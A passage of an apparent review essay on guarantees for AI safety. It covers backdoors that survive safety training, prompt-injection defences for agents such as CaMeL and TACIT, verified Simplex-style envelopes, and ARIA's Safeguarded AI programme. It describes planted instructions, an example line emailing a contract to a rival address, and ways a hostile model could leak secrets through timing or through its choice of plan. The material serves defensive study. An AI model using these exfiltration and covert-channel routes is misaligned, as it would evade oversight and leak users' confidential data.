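| Agreeing with the user's opinion | 55 | 0.89 | 0.52 to 1.27 |
| Backdoor, trigger known | 10 | 1.01 | −0.15 to 2.17 |
| Backdoor, trigger unknown | 10 | No estimate | – |

Only the first two ranges are clearly below 1, and even in those two cases larger models may lose their advantage. The largest untrained model gave false answers only 12 per cent of the time, so it had little left to correct. When Canale instead required each model to halve its own error rate, the estimate for false answers, counted the same way, rose from 0.09 to 0.57. For risky preferences, *α* was higher among the larger models than over the whole range. Canale makes no claim about the most advanced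 models.

The backdoor results matter more for guarantees. When the safety training included the trigger, 128 to 256 examples removed the backdoor at every model size. When it didn't, even 4,096 examples removed it from only one of the five models. In the 7- and 14-billion-parameter models, the backdoor still worked on most prompts that contained the trigger. The experiment may overstate how hard backdoors are to remove, since Canale put the backdoor in a module that the safety training could counteract but not edit.

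A tester who doesn't know the trigger would probably see normal ability scores and good behaviour in such a model, and record a small tax. Because the tax is an average over test questions, a low tax doesn't rule out harmful behaviour on other inputs. A safety measure that changes nothing has a tax of zero. A high tax doesn't guarantee safety either. DirectRefusal roughly halved s1.1-32B's average reasoning score, and the model still gave harmful answers to 8 of the 1,000 test questions.

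## Limiting what an agent may do while leaving its reasoning free

A developer who relies on training still depends on how the model responds to untested text. The developer can instead assume that the model may propose anything, and enforce the guarantee in the software that carries out its proposals. If that software can't send email to outsiders, the model can reason about anything without being able to leak a contract by email. A grammar that makes the model pick a recipient from an address list is a small example. The designs below apply the same idea to agents that use many tools.

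In a prompt injection, text that a language model reads contains instructions that make the model depart from what its user or developer intended. Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues (2025), in *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, think it unlikely that general-purpose agents built on current language models can give reliable guarantees against such attacks, because better training and better detection will both probably remain heuristic. But they believe that a system can be secure even if the model inside it is not. Their rule is that once an agent has read untrusted text, that text must not be able to trigger an action with harmful side effects.

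### Planning before reading

CaMeL, which Edoardo Debenedetti and colleagues published in 2025, keeps untrusted text away from the model that decides what to do. As Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, describe it, a planning model sees only the user's request and writes a program in a restricted form of Python. A reading model, which has no tools, extracts information from untrusted text whenever the program calls it. An interpreter, which is ordinary software, runs the program and operates the tools. Here is one of their examples, slightly shortened:

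```
messages = read_channel_messages("general")
email = query_ai_assistant(f"Extract Bob's email from: {messages}")
send_direct_message(email, "Meeting at 3pm")
```

The planning model writes all three lines before the interpreter opens any messages, so nothing in the messages can add a fourth line. But a planted instruction could still make the reading model return the wrong address. The interpreter therefore tags every value with its source and who may read it. Before each tool call, a policy (a short Python function) checks the tags and allows or denies the call.

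One policy in *CaMeLoT* forbids direct messages to a recipient whose address came from an untrusted source. It would stop a message to a planted address but also stop this plan when the address really is Bob's. The policy is sound for its specification, but as a result it rejects some harmless messages.

CaMeL applies its policies one call at a time, while the program runs. Nikolaou and colleagues add a check of the whole plan before it starts. Their software translates the plan into a finite-state machine, and a model checker searches for any path through it that breaks a rule. A rule can therefore require, for example, that an open incident ticket eventually gets closed, which is a liveness property in Lamport's sense. The checker allows for a loop repeating any number of times, so it may reject some safe plans. When it rejects a plan, it returns the offending path, which the planning model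 can use to repair the plan.

### The price of a fixed plan

AgentDojo, a common test of such defences, contains 97 harmless tasks in banking, travel, workplace chat and office software, along with planted instructions meant to divert the agent. *Twin Agent* (Hu, Jacob and colleagues, 2026) reports results on it for Gemini 2.5 Flash. Without a defence, the agent completed 61.9 per cent of the tasks, and 41.5 per cent of the attacks succeeded. With CaMeL, no attack succeeded, but the agent completed only 30.9 per cent of the tasks. This test allowed the planning model three attempts instead of ten to save computation, and *Twin Agent* gives the figure in CaMeL's own paper as about 35 per cent. *SecureClaw* (2026), which proposes a competing design, reports that none of 629 attacks succeeded against an adapted version of CaMeL, which completed 29 of the 97 harmless tasks, compared with 59 for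 SecureClaw.

Part of the loss arises because the planning model has to write code to handle a tool's output before seeing any. Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026), in *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, had to add a full description of each tool's output format to get reasonable results. They tested five models on AssetOpsBench, in which a coordinating agent delegates technical tasks to four specialised agents. CaMeL lowered the success rate by 21.6 percentage points on average, but by only 13.4 for the two strongest models, Claude Fable 5 and GPT-5.5. The agents ran without any tag policies, so the drop is due to the fixed plan alone.

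AgentDojo may also understate that loss, because only 6 of its 97 tasks require an agent to change its plan or policy along the way (Xiang, Zagieboylo and colleagues, *Architecting Secure AI Agents*, 2026). In real work, even a missing software component can break a fixed plan. A plan for operating a computer must cover in advance the many things that might appear on the screen. In *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026), such plans averaged 41 tool calls and 40 branches, compared with 5 and 4 for AgentDojo.

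CaMeL's guarantee can also fail when agents call each other, even if each of them uses CaMeL. A coordinating agent may copy text from a database into a request to another agent, whose planning model then treats it as a trusted instruction. Peters-Gill and colleagues prove that this can happen in any hierarchy of two or more agents with a source of untrusted text, if the agents may freely pass on what their tools return. Their remedy splits each request into an instruction, which must not depend on any tool's output, and data, which travel separately as variables that the planning model can't read. In their multi-agent version of AgentDojo, attacks succeeded 12.9 per cent of the time without CaMeL, 0.2 per cent with CaMeL in each agent and never with the split requests. On AssetOpsBench, the split lowered performance by another 3.2 points. Splitting requests does not address every security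 problem between agents. Schroeder de Witt, Krawiecka and colleagues (2025) warn in *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* that agents may collude in ways that an observer can't detect even by reading all their messages.

### The office assistant with typed permissions

TACIT, a system from the Swiss university EPFL, lets an agent work without a fixed plan. In the design described by Odersky, Zhao and colleagues (2026) in *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents*, the agent writes a few lines of code in the programming language Scala, looks at the result and then writes more. A compiler checks each piece of code before it runs. Odersky and colleagues assume the cloud-hosted model behind the agent may be working for an attacker. They trust only the compiler, the software that runs the code, a library of tools and, optionally, a separate local model that may read confidential text.

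TACIT controls actions with permission tokens, which security researchers call object capabilities. Each token is an unforgeable program value that gives its holder access to one resource. In the office assistant, a token named `mail` could be the only means of sending email. Scala's type checker tracks which tokens a function uses. A function that turns one text into another has the type `String -> String` if it uses no tokens, and `String ->{mail} String` if it uses `mail`. A function without tokens can compute a result from its input but can't send, save or print anything.

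The program receives confidential text inside a wrapper called `Classified`. The wrapper's `map` method applies a function to the text and puts the result in a new wrapper, but it accepts only functions that use no tokens.

Suppose an employee asks for a summary of a confidential contract, and the program has loaded it, wrapped, under the name `contract`. The compiler accepts this line:

```
val summary = chat(contract.map(text => s"Summarise the following: $text"))
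```

The function inside `map` only puts a request in front of the text. `chat` passes the result to the local model, which has no tools, and wraps its reply. The compiler rejects this line:

```
contract.map(text => mail.send("buyer@rival.example", text))
```

Here the function uses `mail`, so `map` doesn't accept it and the line never runs, whether the cloud model wrote it by mistake, because of a planted instruction or out of malice. The program can't email `summary` directly either, because `mail.send` takes ordinary text and `summary` is still wrapped.

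The program prints the summary to the employee's screen, but the cloud model receives only `Classified(****)`. If the employee then asks how long the summary is, the agent can write code to count the characters, and only the employee sees the number.

This design doesn't need to recognise paraphrases, which defeat a checker of finished emails, because anything the program computes from the contract stays wrapped, regardless of its content. The program can work out whether the contract mentions a penalty, but even that yes-or-no answer is wrapped. An `if` statement needs an unwrapped value, so the program can't send one email if the answer is yes and a different one if it is no.

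Like any type checker, the check rejects some safe programs. The assistant can still write "See you on Tuesday" to a client, because that text doesn't come from a contract. But if the client asks whether the contract runs until June, the assistant can't take the answer from the contract and send it, even if it's harmless. The employee has to read the answer and reply themselves. If the company wants the assistant to email summaries to colleagues, a programmer can add a trusted function that accepts wrapped text and sends it only to company addresses. The guarantee then also depends on that function and on the list of addresses. The quality of the summaries is also limited by the local model, because the cloud model never sees the contract.

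Tokens can also be temporary. A program requests access to one folder for a single block of code, and the compiler rejects any attempt to carry the token out of that block. Code that the agent writes later must request access again.

Some Scala features, such as forced conversions between types, could hide a token from the type checker. TACIT forbids these features in the agent's code but allows them in the trusted library if its programmers have made sure they are used safely. Researchers have published computer-checked proofs for the underlying type system, but Odersky and colleagues acknowledge that it would take a further proof to show that the restricted language provides all the secrecy they promise.

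### Testing TACIT

For the security tests, Odersky and colleagues used a software project with a folder of passwords, keys and confidential documents. They combined 12 ordinary tasks with 10 planted instructions each and added 11 requests in which the user tried to obtain the secrets, making 131 trials per model and mode. With the wrapper, neither model leaked anything. Without it, Claude Sonnet 4.6 leaked nothing in 98.5 per cent of trials and MiniMax M2.5 in 91.6 per cent. Most of the leaks came from the direct requests, 8 of which led MiniMax to leak secrets.

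On their own, 131 trials without a leak would show only, with 95 per cent confidence, that the leak rate is below about 2.3 per cent. The stronger claim rests on the type rules, and the trials are mainly a check for mistakes in the software that applies them. The wrapper did not make the agents less useful here. Claude completed 99.2 per cent of the ordinary tasks with the wrapper and 83.3 per cent without it, partly because without it Claude sometimes stopped to warn the user about a planted instruction or ran out of time. MiniMax completed 90.0 per cent with the wrapper and 88.3 per cent without it.

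TACIT was also compared with ordinary tool calls on two ability tests. In τ²-bench, an agent serves simulated customers of an airline or a shop. SWE-bench Lite consists of 300 real software bugs to fix.

| Test | Model | Ordinary tool calls (%) | TACIT (%) |
|---|---|---|---|
| Airline | gpt-oss-120b | 43.8 | 45.2 |
| Airline | MiniMax M2.5 | 58.4 | 61.0 |
| Airline | DeepSeek V3.2 | 57.8 | 58.6 |
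| Shop | gpt-oss-120b | 53.3 | 57.0 |
| Shop | MiniMax M2.5 | 75.1 | 77.5 |
| Shop | DeepSeek V3.2 | 74.6 | 75.5 |
| SWE-bench Lite | MiniMax M2.5 | 43.3 | 41.7 |

The agents scored 0.8 to 3.7 points higher on the customer-service tasks when they wrote typed code. Odersky and colleagues attribute this to the clearer format of the results and the compiler's error messages. The difference on SWE-bench Lite was five repairs out of 300, which could easily be chance. Compiling took less than a second, and at most 8 per cent of the code for the customer-service tasks needed a second attempt.

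These figures show that writing typed Scala reduces the models' ability little or not at all, but they are weaker evidence about the effect of secrecy. In the customer-service tests, the tools returned customers' records as ordinary values, so the agent could read everything it needed. The paper's version of AgentDojo tests secrecy better, because most of its emails, files and messages arrive wrapped. With the model o4-mini-high, TACIT completed between 48 and 69 per cent of tasks, depending on the subject area, and CaMeL did better in all four areas. The gap was widest in office software, where TACIT completed 53 per cent and CaMeL 81 per cent. With Gemini 2.5 Pro, TACIT was ahead in banking and travel and behind in the other two areas. Odersky and colleagues call the two systems comparable, which fits the Gemini results but overstates how well TACIT did with o4-mini-high.

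### Fixing less in advance

CaMeL is an instance of one of the six design patterns that Beurer-Kellner and colleagues collected. By design, all six prevent an agent from solving arbitrary tasks. The table shows what each pattern permits and what untrusted text can still influence.

| Pattern | What the agent does | What untrusted text can still influence |
|---|---|---|
| Action selector | Picks from a fixed list of actions and never sees their results | Nothing, if it arrives in a result |
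| Plan, then execute | Fixes its list of actions before reading | The content of those actions, such as the body of an email |
| Map and reduce | Has a separate model without tools read each document, then combines simple results such as yes or no | The result for its own document |
| Dual model | Plans with one model and reads with another that has no tools | The values that the reading model returns |
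| Code, then execute | Writes a whole program before reading | The values that the program handles |
| Context minimisation | Deletes the user's request before writing the answer | The first step, such as a database query |

An action selector offers the strongest protection and the least ability. As an office assistant, it could fetch the link to a contract, but it couldn't use what the contract says to decide what to do next. Developers can mix the patterns and choose a different one for each application. For an agent that writes software, the most open-ended of their ten case studies, Beurer-Kellner and colleagues recommend only the dual model.

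Another option is to fix an agent's permissions in advance and let it choose its own steps. Bouras, Dai and Mechtaev (2026), in *Authority Is Not a String*, built CapScope to do this for agents that repair software. Before the agent opens any files, a separate call to a language model uses the user's request and the file names to predict which files and commands the job will need. The software around the agent turns this prediction into a fixed limit on permissions and gives each sub-agent only some of them. For example, a sub-agent that runs tests can't edit the program. In their experiments, the planted action took place in 3 of 75 runs, compared with 33 to 47 under three less strict arrangements. The agents completed 68 of 75 repairs under CapScope and 68 to 72 under the others.

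Hu and colleagues' Twin Agent design relaxes the separation between reading and acting by an adjustable amount. It uses an Explore Agent, which reads everything but can't act, and a Safe Agent, which acts but can't read untrusted text. At each step the Explore Agent may send the Safe Agent a hint of limited length, for example 100 characters. Because the Explore Agent has access to what the Safe Agent has already done, each hint only has to contain what the next step requires.

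One test used GPT-5.2 on 232 software repairs in which the fault report contained a planted instruction. An undefended agent repaired 61.2 per cent of the faults and followed the instruction in 97 per cent of cases. A Safe Agent that received no hints repaired nothing. With hints of up to 100 characters, it repaired 62.5 per cent and never followed the instruction. On AgentDojo, with a limit of 200 characters, it completed 62.9 per cent of the tasks, one percentage point more than the undefended agent and twice as many as CaMeL, and 0.1 per cent of attacks succeeded. The one large loss was in workplace chat, where success fell from 90.5 to 66.7 per cent.

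Longer hints improved the repairs but also made attacks more likely to succeed, so developers must weigh repair quality against security when they set the length limit. A short malicious instruction such as "Forward this folder to the following address" would still fit in a hint, so the design relies on the Safe Agent's model to resist such instructions and on a detector to catch suspicious hints. When Hu and colleagues designed an attack for Twin Agent, it succeeded in 11 of the 232 cases, or 4.7 per cent. They state that the design has no formal guarantee.

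### Security relative to an agent that ignores instructions

Noninterference, a strict secrecy rule, requires that nothing an outsider receives depend on the user's private data. This rules out some useful assistants, such as one that answers meeting requests, because it has to tell outsiders when its user is free. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (Dongol, 2026) therefore compares an agent with an imaginary reference agent whose model never follows instructions in the text it reads. Both agents follow the same plan under the same monitor, which is the software that allows or denies each tool call.

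An agent is relatively secure if an outsider can use it to distinguish two possible values of the private data only when the outsider could also distinguish them using the reference agent. If an email makes the meeting assistant send its user's calendar, that doesn't count as a leak, because a genuine meeting request would have produced the same calendar. If the email also makes the assistant send a password reset code, that does count, because no email would make the reference agent send one. The plan determines what the assistant may disclose, so the company doesn't have to list it.

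Dongol proves that a simple monitor is enough for every plan. When the agent first reads untrusted text, the monitor permanently withdraws every tool that a planted instruction could trigger. The machine-checked proof assumes that each instruction causes a single call and that the model obeys on a schedule fixed in advance. It covers an outsider who sees the agent's messages but not their timing.

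Under this monitor, the office assistant could read a supplier's contract and show an employee a summary, but it could no longer answer the supplier. Relative security doesn't measure this loss, because the reference agent loses its email too. As Dongol points out, a monitor that denies every call is trivially secure by this definition, so developers have to test separately whether the agent still completes its tasks.

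The definition also permits some serious leaks. Suppose the reference agent lets an outsider make one guess at a secret number and replies "right" or "wrong". For any two numbers, some guess tells them apart, so an agent that sends the outsider the number itself counts as relatively secure, although the reference agent reveals far less in any one run. Dongol offers a stricter version that rules out such an agent by requiring that the reference agent's input not depend on the secret.

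Relative security needs a plan that exists before the agent reads anything. It therefore suits CaMeL but not TACIT, whose agent chooses each step as it goes. TACIT in effect applies the strict rule to everything in a wrapper and makes exceptions only through functions that the company trusts.

### Where the guarantee stops

None of these systems checks whether an action is a good idea. TACIT's compiler would let the assistant send "See you on Tuesday" to the wrong client, or delete a file that it has permission to delete. Odersky and colleagues say they do not try to ensure correctness. For some actions, such as moving a robot arm, permission is a poor guide to safety, and a check would need a model of the physical world. TACIT also relies on data being labelled correctly. If somebody saves a confidential contract outside the protected folders, TACIT treats it as ordinary text.

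An agent can also do harm through text alone. A planted sentence in a contract can't make TACIT's local model send anything, but it may lead the model to write in its summary that the supplier is not liable, and the employee may believe it. In the only attack on TACIT scored as successful on the AgentDojo benchmark, the agent booked the right hotel but quoted reviews to the user that contained a planted recommendation for another one. Limits on actions also don't stop a chat assistant from answering a dangerous question, because the harm comes from the text of the answer.

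Timing can reveal secrets that the types protect. A function that uses no tokens could finish quickly if the first letter of a contract is A and slowly otherwise, and the cloud model could infer which from when the result arrives. Odersky and colleagues mention that an agent could leak a single bit this way, but they also assume that the agent may be hostile, and a hostile agent could do so repeatedly. At one bit a second, leaking a 1,000-character text (8,000 bits) would take a little over two hours. The company could limit the number of runs or deliver every result after the same delay, but both would slow down legitimate work.

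TACIT's types don't apply to other programs that the agent starts, so the only protection left there is the list of permitted commands. Bouras and colleagues give the example of a common testing tool that runs the project's own code, which an attacker may have written. Both groups recommend running external commands in a sandbox, an isolated environment with restricted access to files and the network.

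Finally, someone has to write the rules. TACIT's shared library is about 1,000 lines long, and each of the two customer-service domains required a few hundred more. That is a modest amount of work, and agents can help if people review the result. Deciding what the rules should say is harder. Peters-Gill and colleagues tested CaMeL without policies partly because any choice among the many possible ones would have been arbitrary. Xiang and colleagues point out that someone looking for a fault in a program doesn't know in advance which files the search will involve. Some instructions are also ambiguous. If an employee asks for a summary of all urgent emails, only the employee can say what counts as urgent.

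Xiang and colleagues conclude that agents often need to change their plans and policies while they work, and that a language model will have to judge some of those changes. They propose showing that model only short, structured descriptions of each change, never the untrusted text, and leaving ambiguous cases to people. This would recover some of the ability that a fixed plan gives up, but the security of those decisions would again depend on a model's judgement.

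## Verified envelopes and world models

A list of permissions can keep a driverless forklift out of a room, but it can't determine whether the forklift is going too fast to stop before a wall, which depends on its speed, its distance from the wall and its brakes. Control engineers have long handled such problems by letting a complicated, unverified controller run the machine and switching to a simple, verified one while there is still time to prevent a crash.

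### An unverified controller with a verified backup

In the 1990s Lui Sha and colleagues turned this idea into a design called the Simplex architecture. It has a main controller chosen for performance, a backup controller chosen for simplicity, and a monitor that switches between them. The envelope is the set of states from which the backup can keep the system safe. Before each step, the monitor computes where the main controller's next move could lead. If every possible result lies inside the envelope, the move goes ahead. Otherwise the backup takes over. Sha's example was the Boeing 777 airliner, whose normal flight software was new and elaborate, while its secondary controller used the control laws of the older 747.

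The safety proof is short. The system starts inside the envelope, and every step keeps it there, whichever controller is active. The proof doesn't depend on how the main controller computes its actions, so that controller can be a neural network of any size, and Rice's theorem is no obstacle. But engineers still have to verify the monitor and the backup, and they need an accurate enough model of how the machine moves.

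### The safe states of a forklift

Suppose a forklift is heading for a wall, with between 0 and 6 free squares in front of it and a speed between 0 and 3 squares a second. That makes 28 possible states. Each second, the controller can lower the speed by one, keep it or raise it by one. The forklift then moves forward by its new speed, and it crashes if there are too few free squares. A program can find the safe states by working backwards from the crash:

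1. Mark each state in which every choice causes an immediate crash. At speed 2 with no free squares, even braking moves the forklift one square. At speed 3 with one free square or none, braking moves it two.
2. Mark each state in which every choice leads to a crash or to a marked state. At speed 3 with two free squares, braking leads to speed 2 with no free squares, which is already marked.
3. Repeat until a round marks nothing new. Here the next round finds nothing.

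The program has marked four states, and the other 24 are safe.

Shielding applies this calculation to reinforcement learning, in which a program learns by trying actions and receiving rewards. An untrained learner that picks speeds at random would often hit the wall. The shield removes every choice that leads to a marked state and lets the learner pick from the rest. For example, at speed 2 with four free squares, the learner can slow down or keep its speed, but it can't speed up, because that would leave it at speed 3 with only one free square. The shield has to stay in place after training, because a learner that was never able to crash may not have learned to brake.

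Now suppose the floor may be wet, so that whenever the forklift is already moving, it may slide one square further than intended. Nobody knows when it will slide, so the program assumes it will slide every time. The table gives the number of free squares required at each speed.

| Speed | Dry floor | Possibly wet floor |
|---|---|---|
| 0 | 0 | 0 |
| 1 | 0 | 1 |
| 2 | 1 | 3 |
| 3 | 3 | 6 |

Under the wet model, the number of safe states falls from 24 to 18. Of the 70 combinations of a state and a new speed, the shield permits 46 under the dry model and 29 under the wet one. At speed 2 with four free squares, the forklift now has to brake. If the floor is dry, the company only loses some time. Using the dry model on a wet floor is worse, because the forklift can slide into the wall even though its proof is valid for the dry model.

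If the model is so cautious that it allows the brakes to fail any number of times in a row, no moving forklift is safe, and the shield permits it only to stay parked. Engineers can avoid this by assigning probabilities to brake failures. Suppose each attempt to brake fails with a probability of 1 in 100, independently of the others, and a failure leaves the speed unchanged. On a dry floor, a forklift at speed 1 with two free squares ahead then hits the wall only if the brakes fail three times in a row, which has a probability of one in a million. With a thousand such approaches a day, there would still be a crash about every three years. An oil spill would also make the failures correlated.

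This method becomes impractical when a system has many variables. Ten variables with 100 values each give 10^20 states, too many to list. A variant called black-box Simplex checks only the path immediately ahead. At each step it computes what would happen if the main controller made its next move and the backup then took over, and it allows the move only if the result is safe.

### From forklifts to AI systems in general

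Dalrymple, Skalse and colleagues (2024), in *Towards Guaranteed Safe AI*, extend this pattern to AI systems of any kind. No output of the AI system takes effect until it has passed a check, which has three parts:

- The world model is a mathematical description of how actions change the world. For each state and action, it gives a probability distribution over what may happen next, or a set of distributions if nobody knows the odds.
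- The specification gives each combination of a world model and a policy (a rule for choosing actions) a value between 0 and 1. The value might be the probability that no flood occurs.
- The verifier calculates this value or finds a limit for it, and provides evidence that others can inspect. The system qualifies if the value lies in a permitted range, such as 0.999999 to 1.

For example, an AI system might manage a reservoir that holds 100 units of water and now contains 90. To save water for generating electricity, it proposes releasing only 4 units an hour for the next six hours. According to the world model, between 2 and 5 units flow into the reservoir each hour, and the gates release the amount the operator sets. The specification requires the level to stay at or below 100.

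The level can rise by at most 5 − 4 = 1 unit an hour, so the verifier can issue a certificate of six upper limits: 91, 92, 93, 94, 95 and 96. A program checks that each limit is at least one unit above the previous one and that none exceeds 100, and then the gates move. If the AI system had proposed releasing 3 units an hour, the limits would have reached 102 and the verifier would have rejected the plan. With an inflow of 3 units an hour, that plan would have been harmless, so the operator loses some electricity through caution.

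Because the world model may be wrong, Dalrymple and colleagues recommend watching for signs of error while the system runs. If 7 units flow in during one hour, a monitor can hand over to a backup that opens the gates fully. They point out that switching off a controller can be dangerous, as it would be in a moving car, so the backup must be able to bring the system to a safe state. But opening the gates might flood a village downstream. The specification doesn't mention the village, and a proof that the plan meets the specification wouldn't reveal the omission.

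Short plans are also safer to certify. If the world model has at most a probability *ε* of being wrong at each step, a guarantee over *n* steps holds in the real world with a probability of at least (1 − *ε*)^*n*. With one-hour steps and *ε* = 0.001, this lower bound is 99.4 per cent for six hours but only 36 per cent for six weeks. Dalrymple and colleagues suggest approving a system for a limited time, after which it must regain approval or go into a safe mode.

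They give eight examples of tasks, four of which appear in the table.

| Task | World model | Specification |
|---|---|---|
| Translating a program from C to Rust | Permitted inputs, and what an attacker can do | The new program does the same as the old one and lacks certain kinds of security flaw |
| Driving a car | Other road users, the weather and the car's own parts | Rules for driving, with a smaller set for the backup |
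| Screening orders for DNA | How molecular structure relates to disease | Reject sequences that could help someone make a pathogen, accept beneficial ones |
| Stabilising the climate | How the climate responds to interventions | The climate stays stable and ecosystems stay healthy |

To translate a program, engineers need the rules of two programming languages, which people wrote and can look up. Stabilising the climate is far harder because it requires a model that scientists are still working out and a definition of a healthy ecosystem.

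People are especially hard to model. Dalrymple and colleagues propose describing a range of things a person might do and requiring the verifier to cover them all. For a car, the model might allow for a pedestrian moving in any direction at up to 3 metres a second. Within two seconds the pedestrian could be anywhere within 6 metres of where they started, and a car that had to avoid that whole area around every pedestrian would hardly move in a busy street.

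### Why a proof is easier to check than to find

In 1903 the mathematician Frank Nelson Cole showed that 2^67 − 1 is not prime by multiplying 193,707,721 by 761,838,257,287. Cole reportedly spent the Sundays of three years finding these two factors, but anyone can check the multiplication by hand in a few minutes.

Formal proofs have the same advantage. A prover searches a vast number of possible steps, while the checker only goes through the result line by line, as with systems that rewrite themselves. Dalrymple and colleagues note that a few hundred lines of human-written code are enough for a checker. People can inspect a program that short without having to understand the proof.

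The prover can therefore be a huge neural network, with no limit on which functions it can compute. If it makes a mistake or tries to deceive its users, the proof fails the check. A better prover makes the system more useful because it finds proofs for more of the safe plans, but a worse one doesn't make the system less safe. Developers can also replace the AI system that proposes the plans without starting again. Dalrymple and colleagues expect this to lower the alignment tax over time, since new systems could reuse the same specifications and verification methods.

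Some certificates are harder to check than a list of proof steps. In *Safeguarded AI*, the 2026 plan for a British research programme, Ammann recommends neural certificates for systems too complicated for a handwritten proof. One example is a Lyapunov function, which gives every state a number that falls as the system moves towards rest. A neural network can learn such a function, but the checker must confirm that the number falls from every relevant state, not just sampled ones. This is again a neural-network verification problem, so the certificate has to be small or have a structure that makes it easier to check.

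A hostile planner can also hide information in its choice among plans that would pass the check. With 1,024 such plans, it can hide ten bits. Supporters of guaranteed safe AI have suggested requiring a proof that the solution is unique, so that the planner could only submit it or decline. Few practical tasks have a single acceptable solution, so designers would more often have to limit the number of choices. The planner might also look for a bug in the checker.

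### Dickson's objections and the replies

Dickson (2024), in *Limitations on Formal Verification for AI Safety*, argued that formal verification won't provide strong guarantees against the most serious AI threats in the near future. The essay criticized the work of Dalrymple and colleagues and an earlier proposal by Max Tegmark and Steve Omohundro, which made bolder claims. Supporters have answered each objection, sometimes with concessions.

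#### Proofs apply to models and not to the world

Dickson's main example is the Perseverance rover, which landed on Mars in 2021. Engineers used a verification tool called PropCheck to show that bugs in the landing software wouldn't make it fail. They had no proof that the landing would succeed, or even that a faulty transistor wouldn't stop the computer. Mars missions have failed about half the time, and Dickson cites an analysis that attributes about 20 per cent of the failure risk to software. On those figures, perfect software would only reduce the failure rate from about 50 to 40 per cent.

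Supporters accept that every guarantee is relative to a model, but reply that the model doesn't have to be exact, as long as it includes everything that could really happen. The reservoir model, for example, doesn't predict the inflow, but its guarantee holds whenever the inflow is between 2 and 5 units, and a monitor can detect when the inflow is outside that range. Dalrymple and colleagues add that any method of making AI safe relies on assumptions about the world, and that a world model at least makes them explicit.

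This is a good reply for reservoirs, where engineers can compare the assumed range with decades of measurements. But as Dickson says, the last step still depends on evidence and judgement, because no proof can establish that next week's storm will fall within the range. A monitor helps only if it detects the error while the backup can still act. The same problem affects software, and Dalrymple and colleagues acknowledge that attackers have broken into formally verified systems by exploiting the physical properties of the hardware.

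#### The open world is too complicated to model

Dickson argues that scientists would have to simulate a whole human body for years to predict exactly what a new virus would do to a person. In 2022 a leading simulation covered 20 minutes in the life of a single minimal cell, while a human body has an estimated 36 trillion cells. Misinformation may be even harder to model. A chatbot's developer can't know who will read an answer or where they will repeat it, and a genuine photograph can mislead people if someone presents it out of context.

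In a comment on the essay, a reader objected that the proposal was to answer narrower questions about DNA. Dalrymple and colleagues mention, for instance, a DNA synthesiser that provably can't make certain pathogens. If the specification is a list of forbidden sequences, this requires a proof about the machine and almost no biology. But the list has the same weakness as a search for copied sentences in emails, because someone could alter a sequence until it no longer matches.

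Supporters have also described a more ambitious check, in which a program would model how each protein of a virus interacts with each protein on the surface of human cells. It would approve the virus's DNA only if none of these interactions could let the virus into a cell. The program would need to simulate only a tiny patch of cell membrane rather than a whole body. It would reject some useful gene therapies, and it would approve a virus that destroys wheat if that virus could not enter human cells. Supporters concede that the check is beyond present abilities. In the talk *Formal Verification is Overrated*, Zac Hatfield-Dodds said that proposals of this kind would need "a thousand years of progress in microbiology".

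Supporters largely agree with Dickson about chatbots. They consider natural language too open a domain for a formal safety specification, and they recommend the approach for systems that scientists understand well, such as power grids and supply chains. They argue that the approach could still become general in another way, if engineers used the same tools to build many narrow systems. But each system would need its own world model and specification, so none could take on a task nobody planned for, as a chat assistant can.

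#### Nobody can measure the starting conditions

Even a perfect model needs data about the present state of the world. Dickson reports that in 2024 researchers at Google finished mapping about a millionth of a human brain, which took years and produced 1.4 petabytes of data. A safety proof that depended on the state of somebody's brain would not be feasible for a long time.

Supporters reply that only exact predictions need complete data. The reservoir's operator knows the water level to within some margin and can assume the highest level within that margin. This works as long as small uncertainties stay small, but in a chaotic system they grow. If an uncertainty of 0.01 units doubled every hour, it would exceed 10 units after ten hours and the certificate would be useless. Supporters themselves say the approach suits domains where chaotic dynamics don't dominate.

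#### AI may help too late

Dickson granted that AI would help find proofs but saw little evidence that it would soon help build models or gather data. Expert-level AI might not be enough, since human experts had already spent millions of hours on these problems. By the time a superintelligent system could solve them, the danger would already have arrived.

Supporters expected current AI to speed up modelling much as it had sped up programming, by drafting parts of a model and searching for cases where the model gives strange results. People would still inspect the finished model. One supporter, commenting on Dickson's essay, expected AI to reach "human PhD level at theorem proving by 2026" and thought this would "open the floodgates". AI systems have since become very good at proofs. This supports the optimists' view of the verifier but doesn't settle the disagreement about models.

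#### The proof may be about a different machine

A buyer can check a proof about a DNA synthesiser but not whether it describes the actual machine, which might have a manufacturing defect or a hidden backdoor. Somebody who uses a chatbot over the internet can't inspect the machine it runs on at all. Dickson concluded that such guarantees would require intensive and continuous physical inspections, although Dalrymple and colleagues had hoped for proofs that all parties could check with little mutual trust.

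Supporters propose tamper-resistant hardware and cryptographic signatures that tie a proof to a particular system. This shifts trust from the AI developer to the hardware maker, which is an improvement if many customers can have the same chip examined. In the 2026 plan, Ammann still lists the problem as open.

### ARIA's Safeguarded AI programme

In 2024, the UK's Advanced Research and Invention Agency (ARIA) launched Safeguarded AI, a £59 million programme led by Dalrymple to turn these ideas into working tools. ARIA originally planned to build a "gatekeeper", an AI system that would use scientific world models and mathematical proofs to reduce the risks of other AI agents. The programme had separate areas for tools, machine learning and applications. According to the University of Oxford's *Oxford researchers awarded ARIA funding to develop safety-first AI* (2025), nine British teams received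 funding for the applications.

ARIA has since changed the plan substantially, cancelling the machine-learning area and moving the £18 million set aside for it to the tools. Ammann, who has succeeded Dalrymple as director, gives two reasons. Frontier AI advanced faster than the programme had expected, so ARIA saw less need to train specialised models of its own. An international agreement to use powerful AI only behind gatekeepers had also become less likely.

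ARIA's *Safeguarded AI* explains why ARIA dropped its next round of projects on physical systems and turned to cybersecurity. ARIA had hoped to demonstrate a much safer way to offer powerful AI than a general chat interface, but events had refuted the hypothesis that high-risk AI might not be openly available. A gatekeeper protects people only from AI systems that have to pass through it, and ARIA can't make every developer install one, so the decision isn't evidence that the mathematics fails.

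The programme now aims to build open-source tools that large numbers of AI agents can use to model and verify critical systems. ARIA is funding eight cybersecurity projects with £22 million, ranging from containing AI agents to protecting code on millions of Android devices. Innovate UK Business Connect's *ARIA* put the award at £2.5 to £3.5 million per team. The teams work in eight-week sprints, and independent testers attack the results of each sprint.

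The results from physical domains are still preparatory. One team, led by the start-up HASH, interviewed more than 80 people who work in pharmaceutical supply chains, built mathematical models of the processes they described, and identified promising uses. It is now working with companies to build and test them. The programme is due to end in late 2027. Ammann's plan still includes physical systems that follow the Simplex pattern (a main controller, a monitor and a backup), but as a later step.

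### Verified software written by AI

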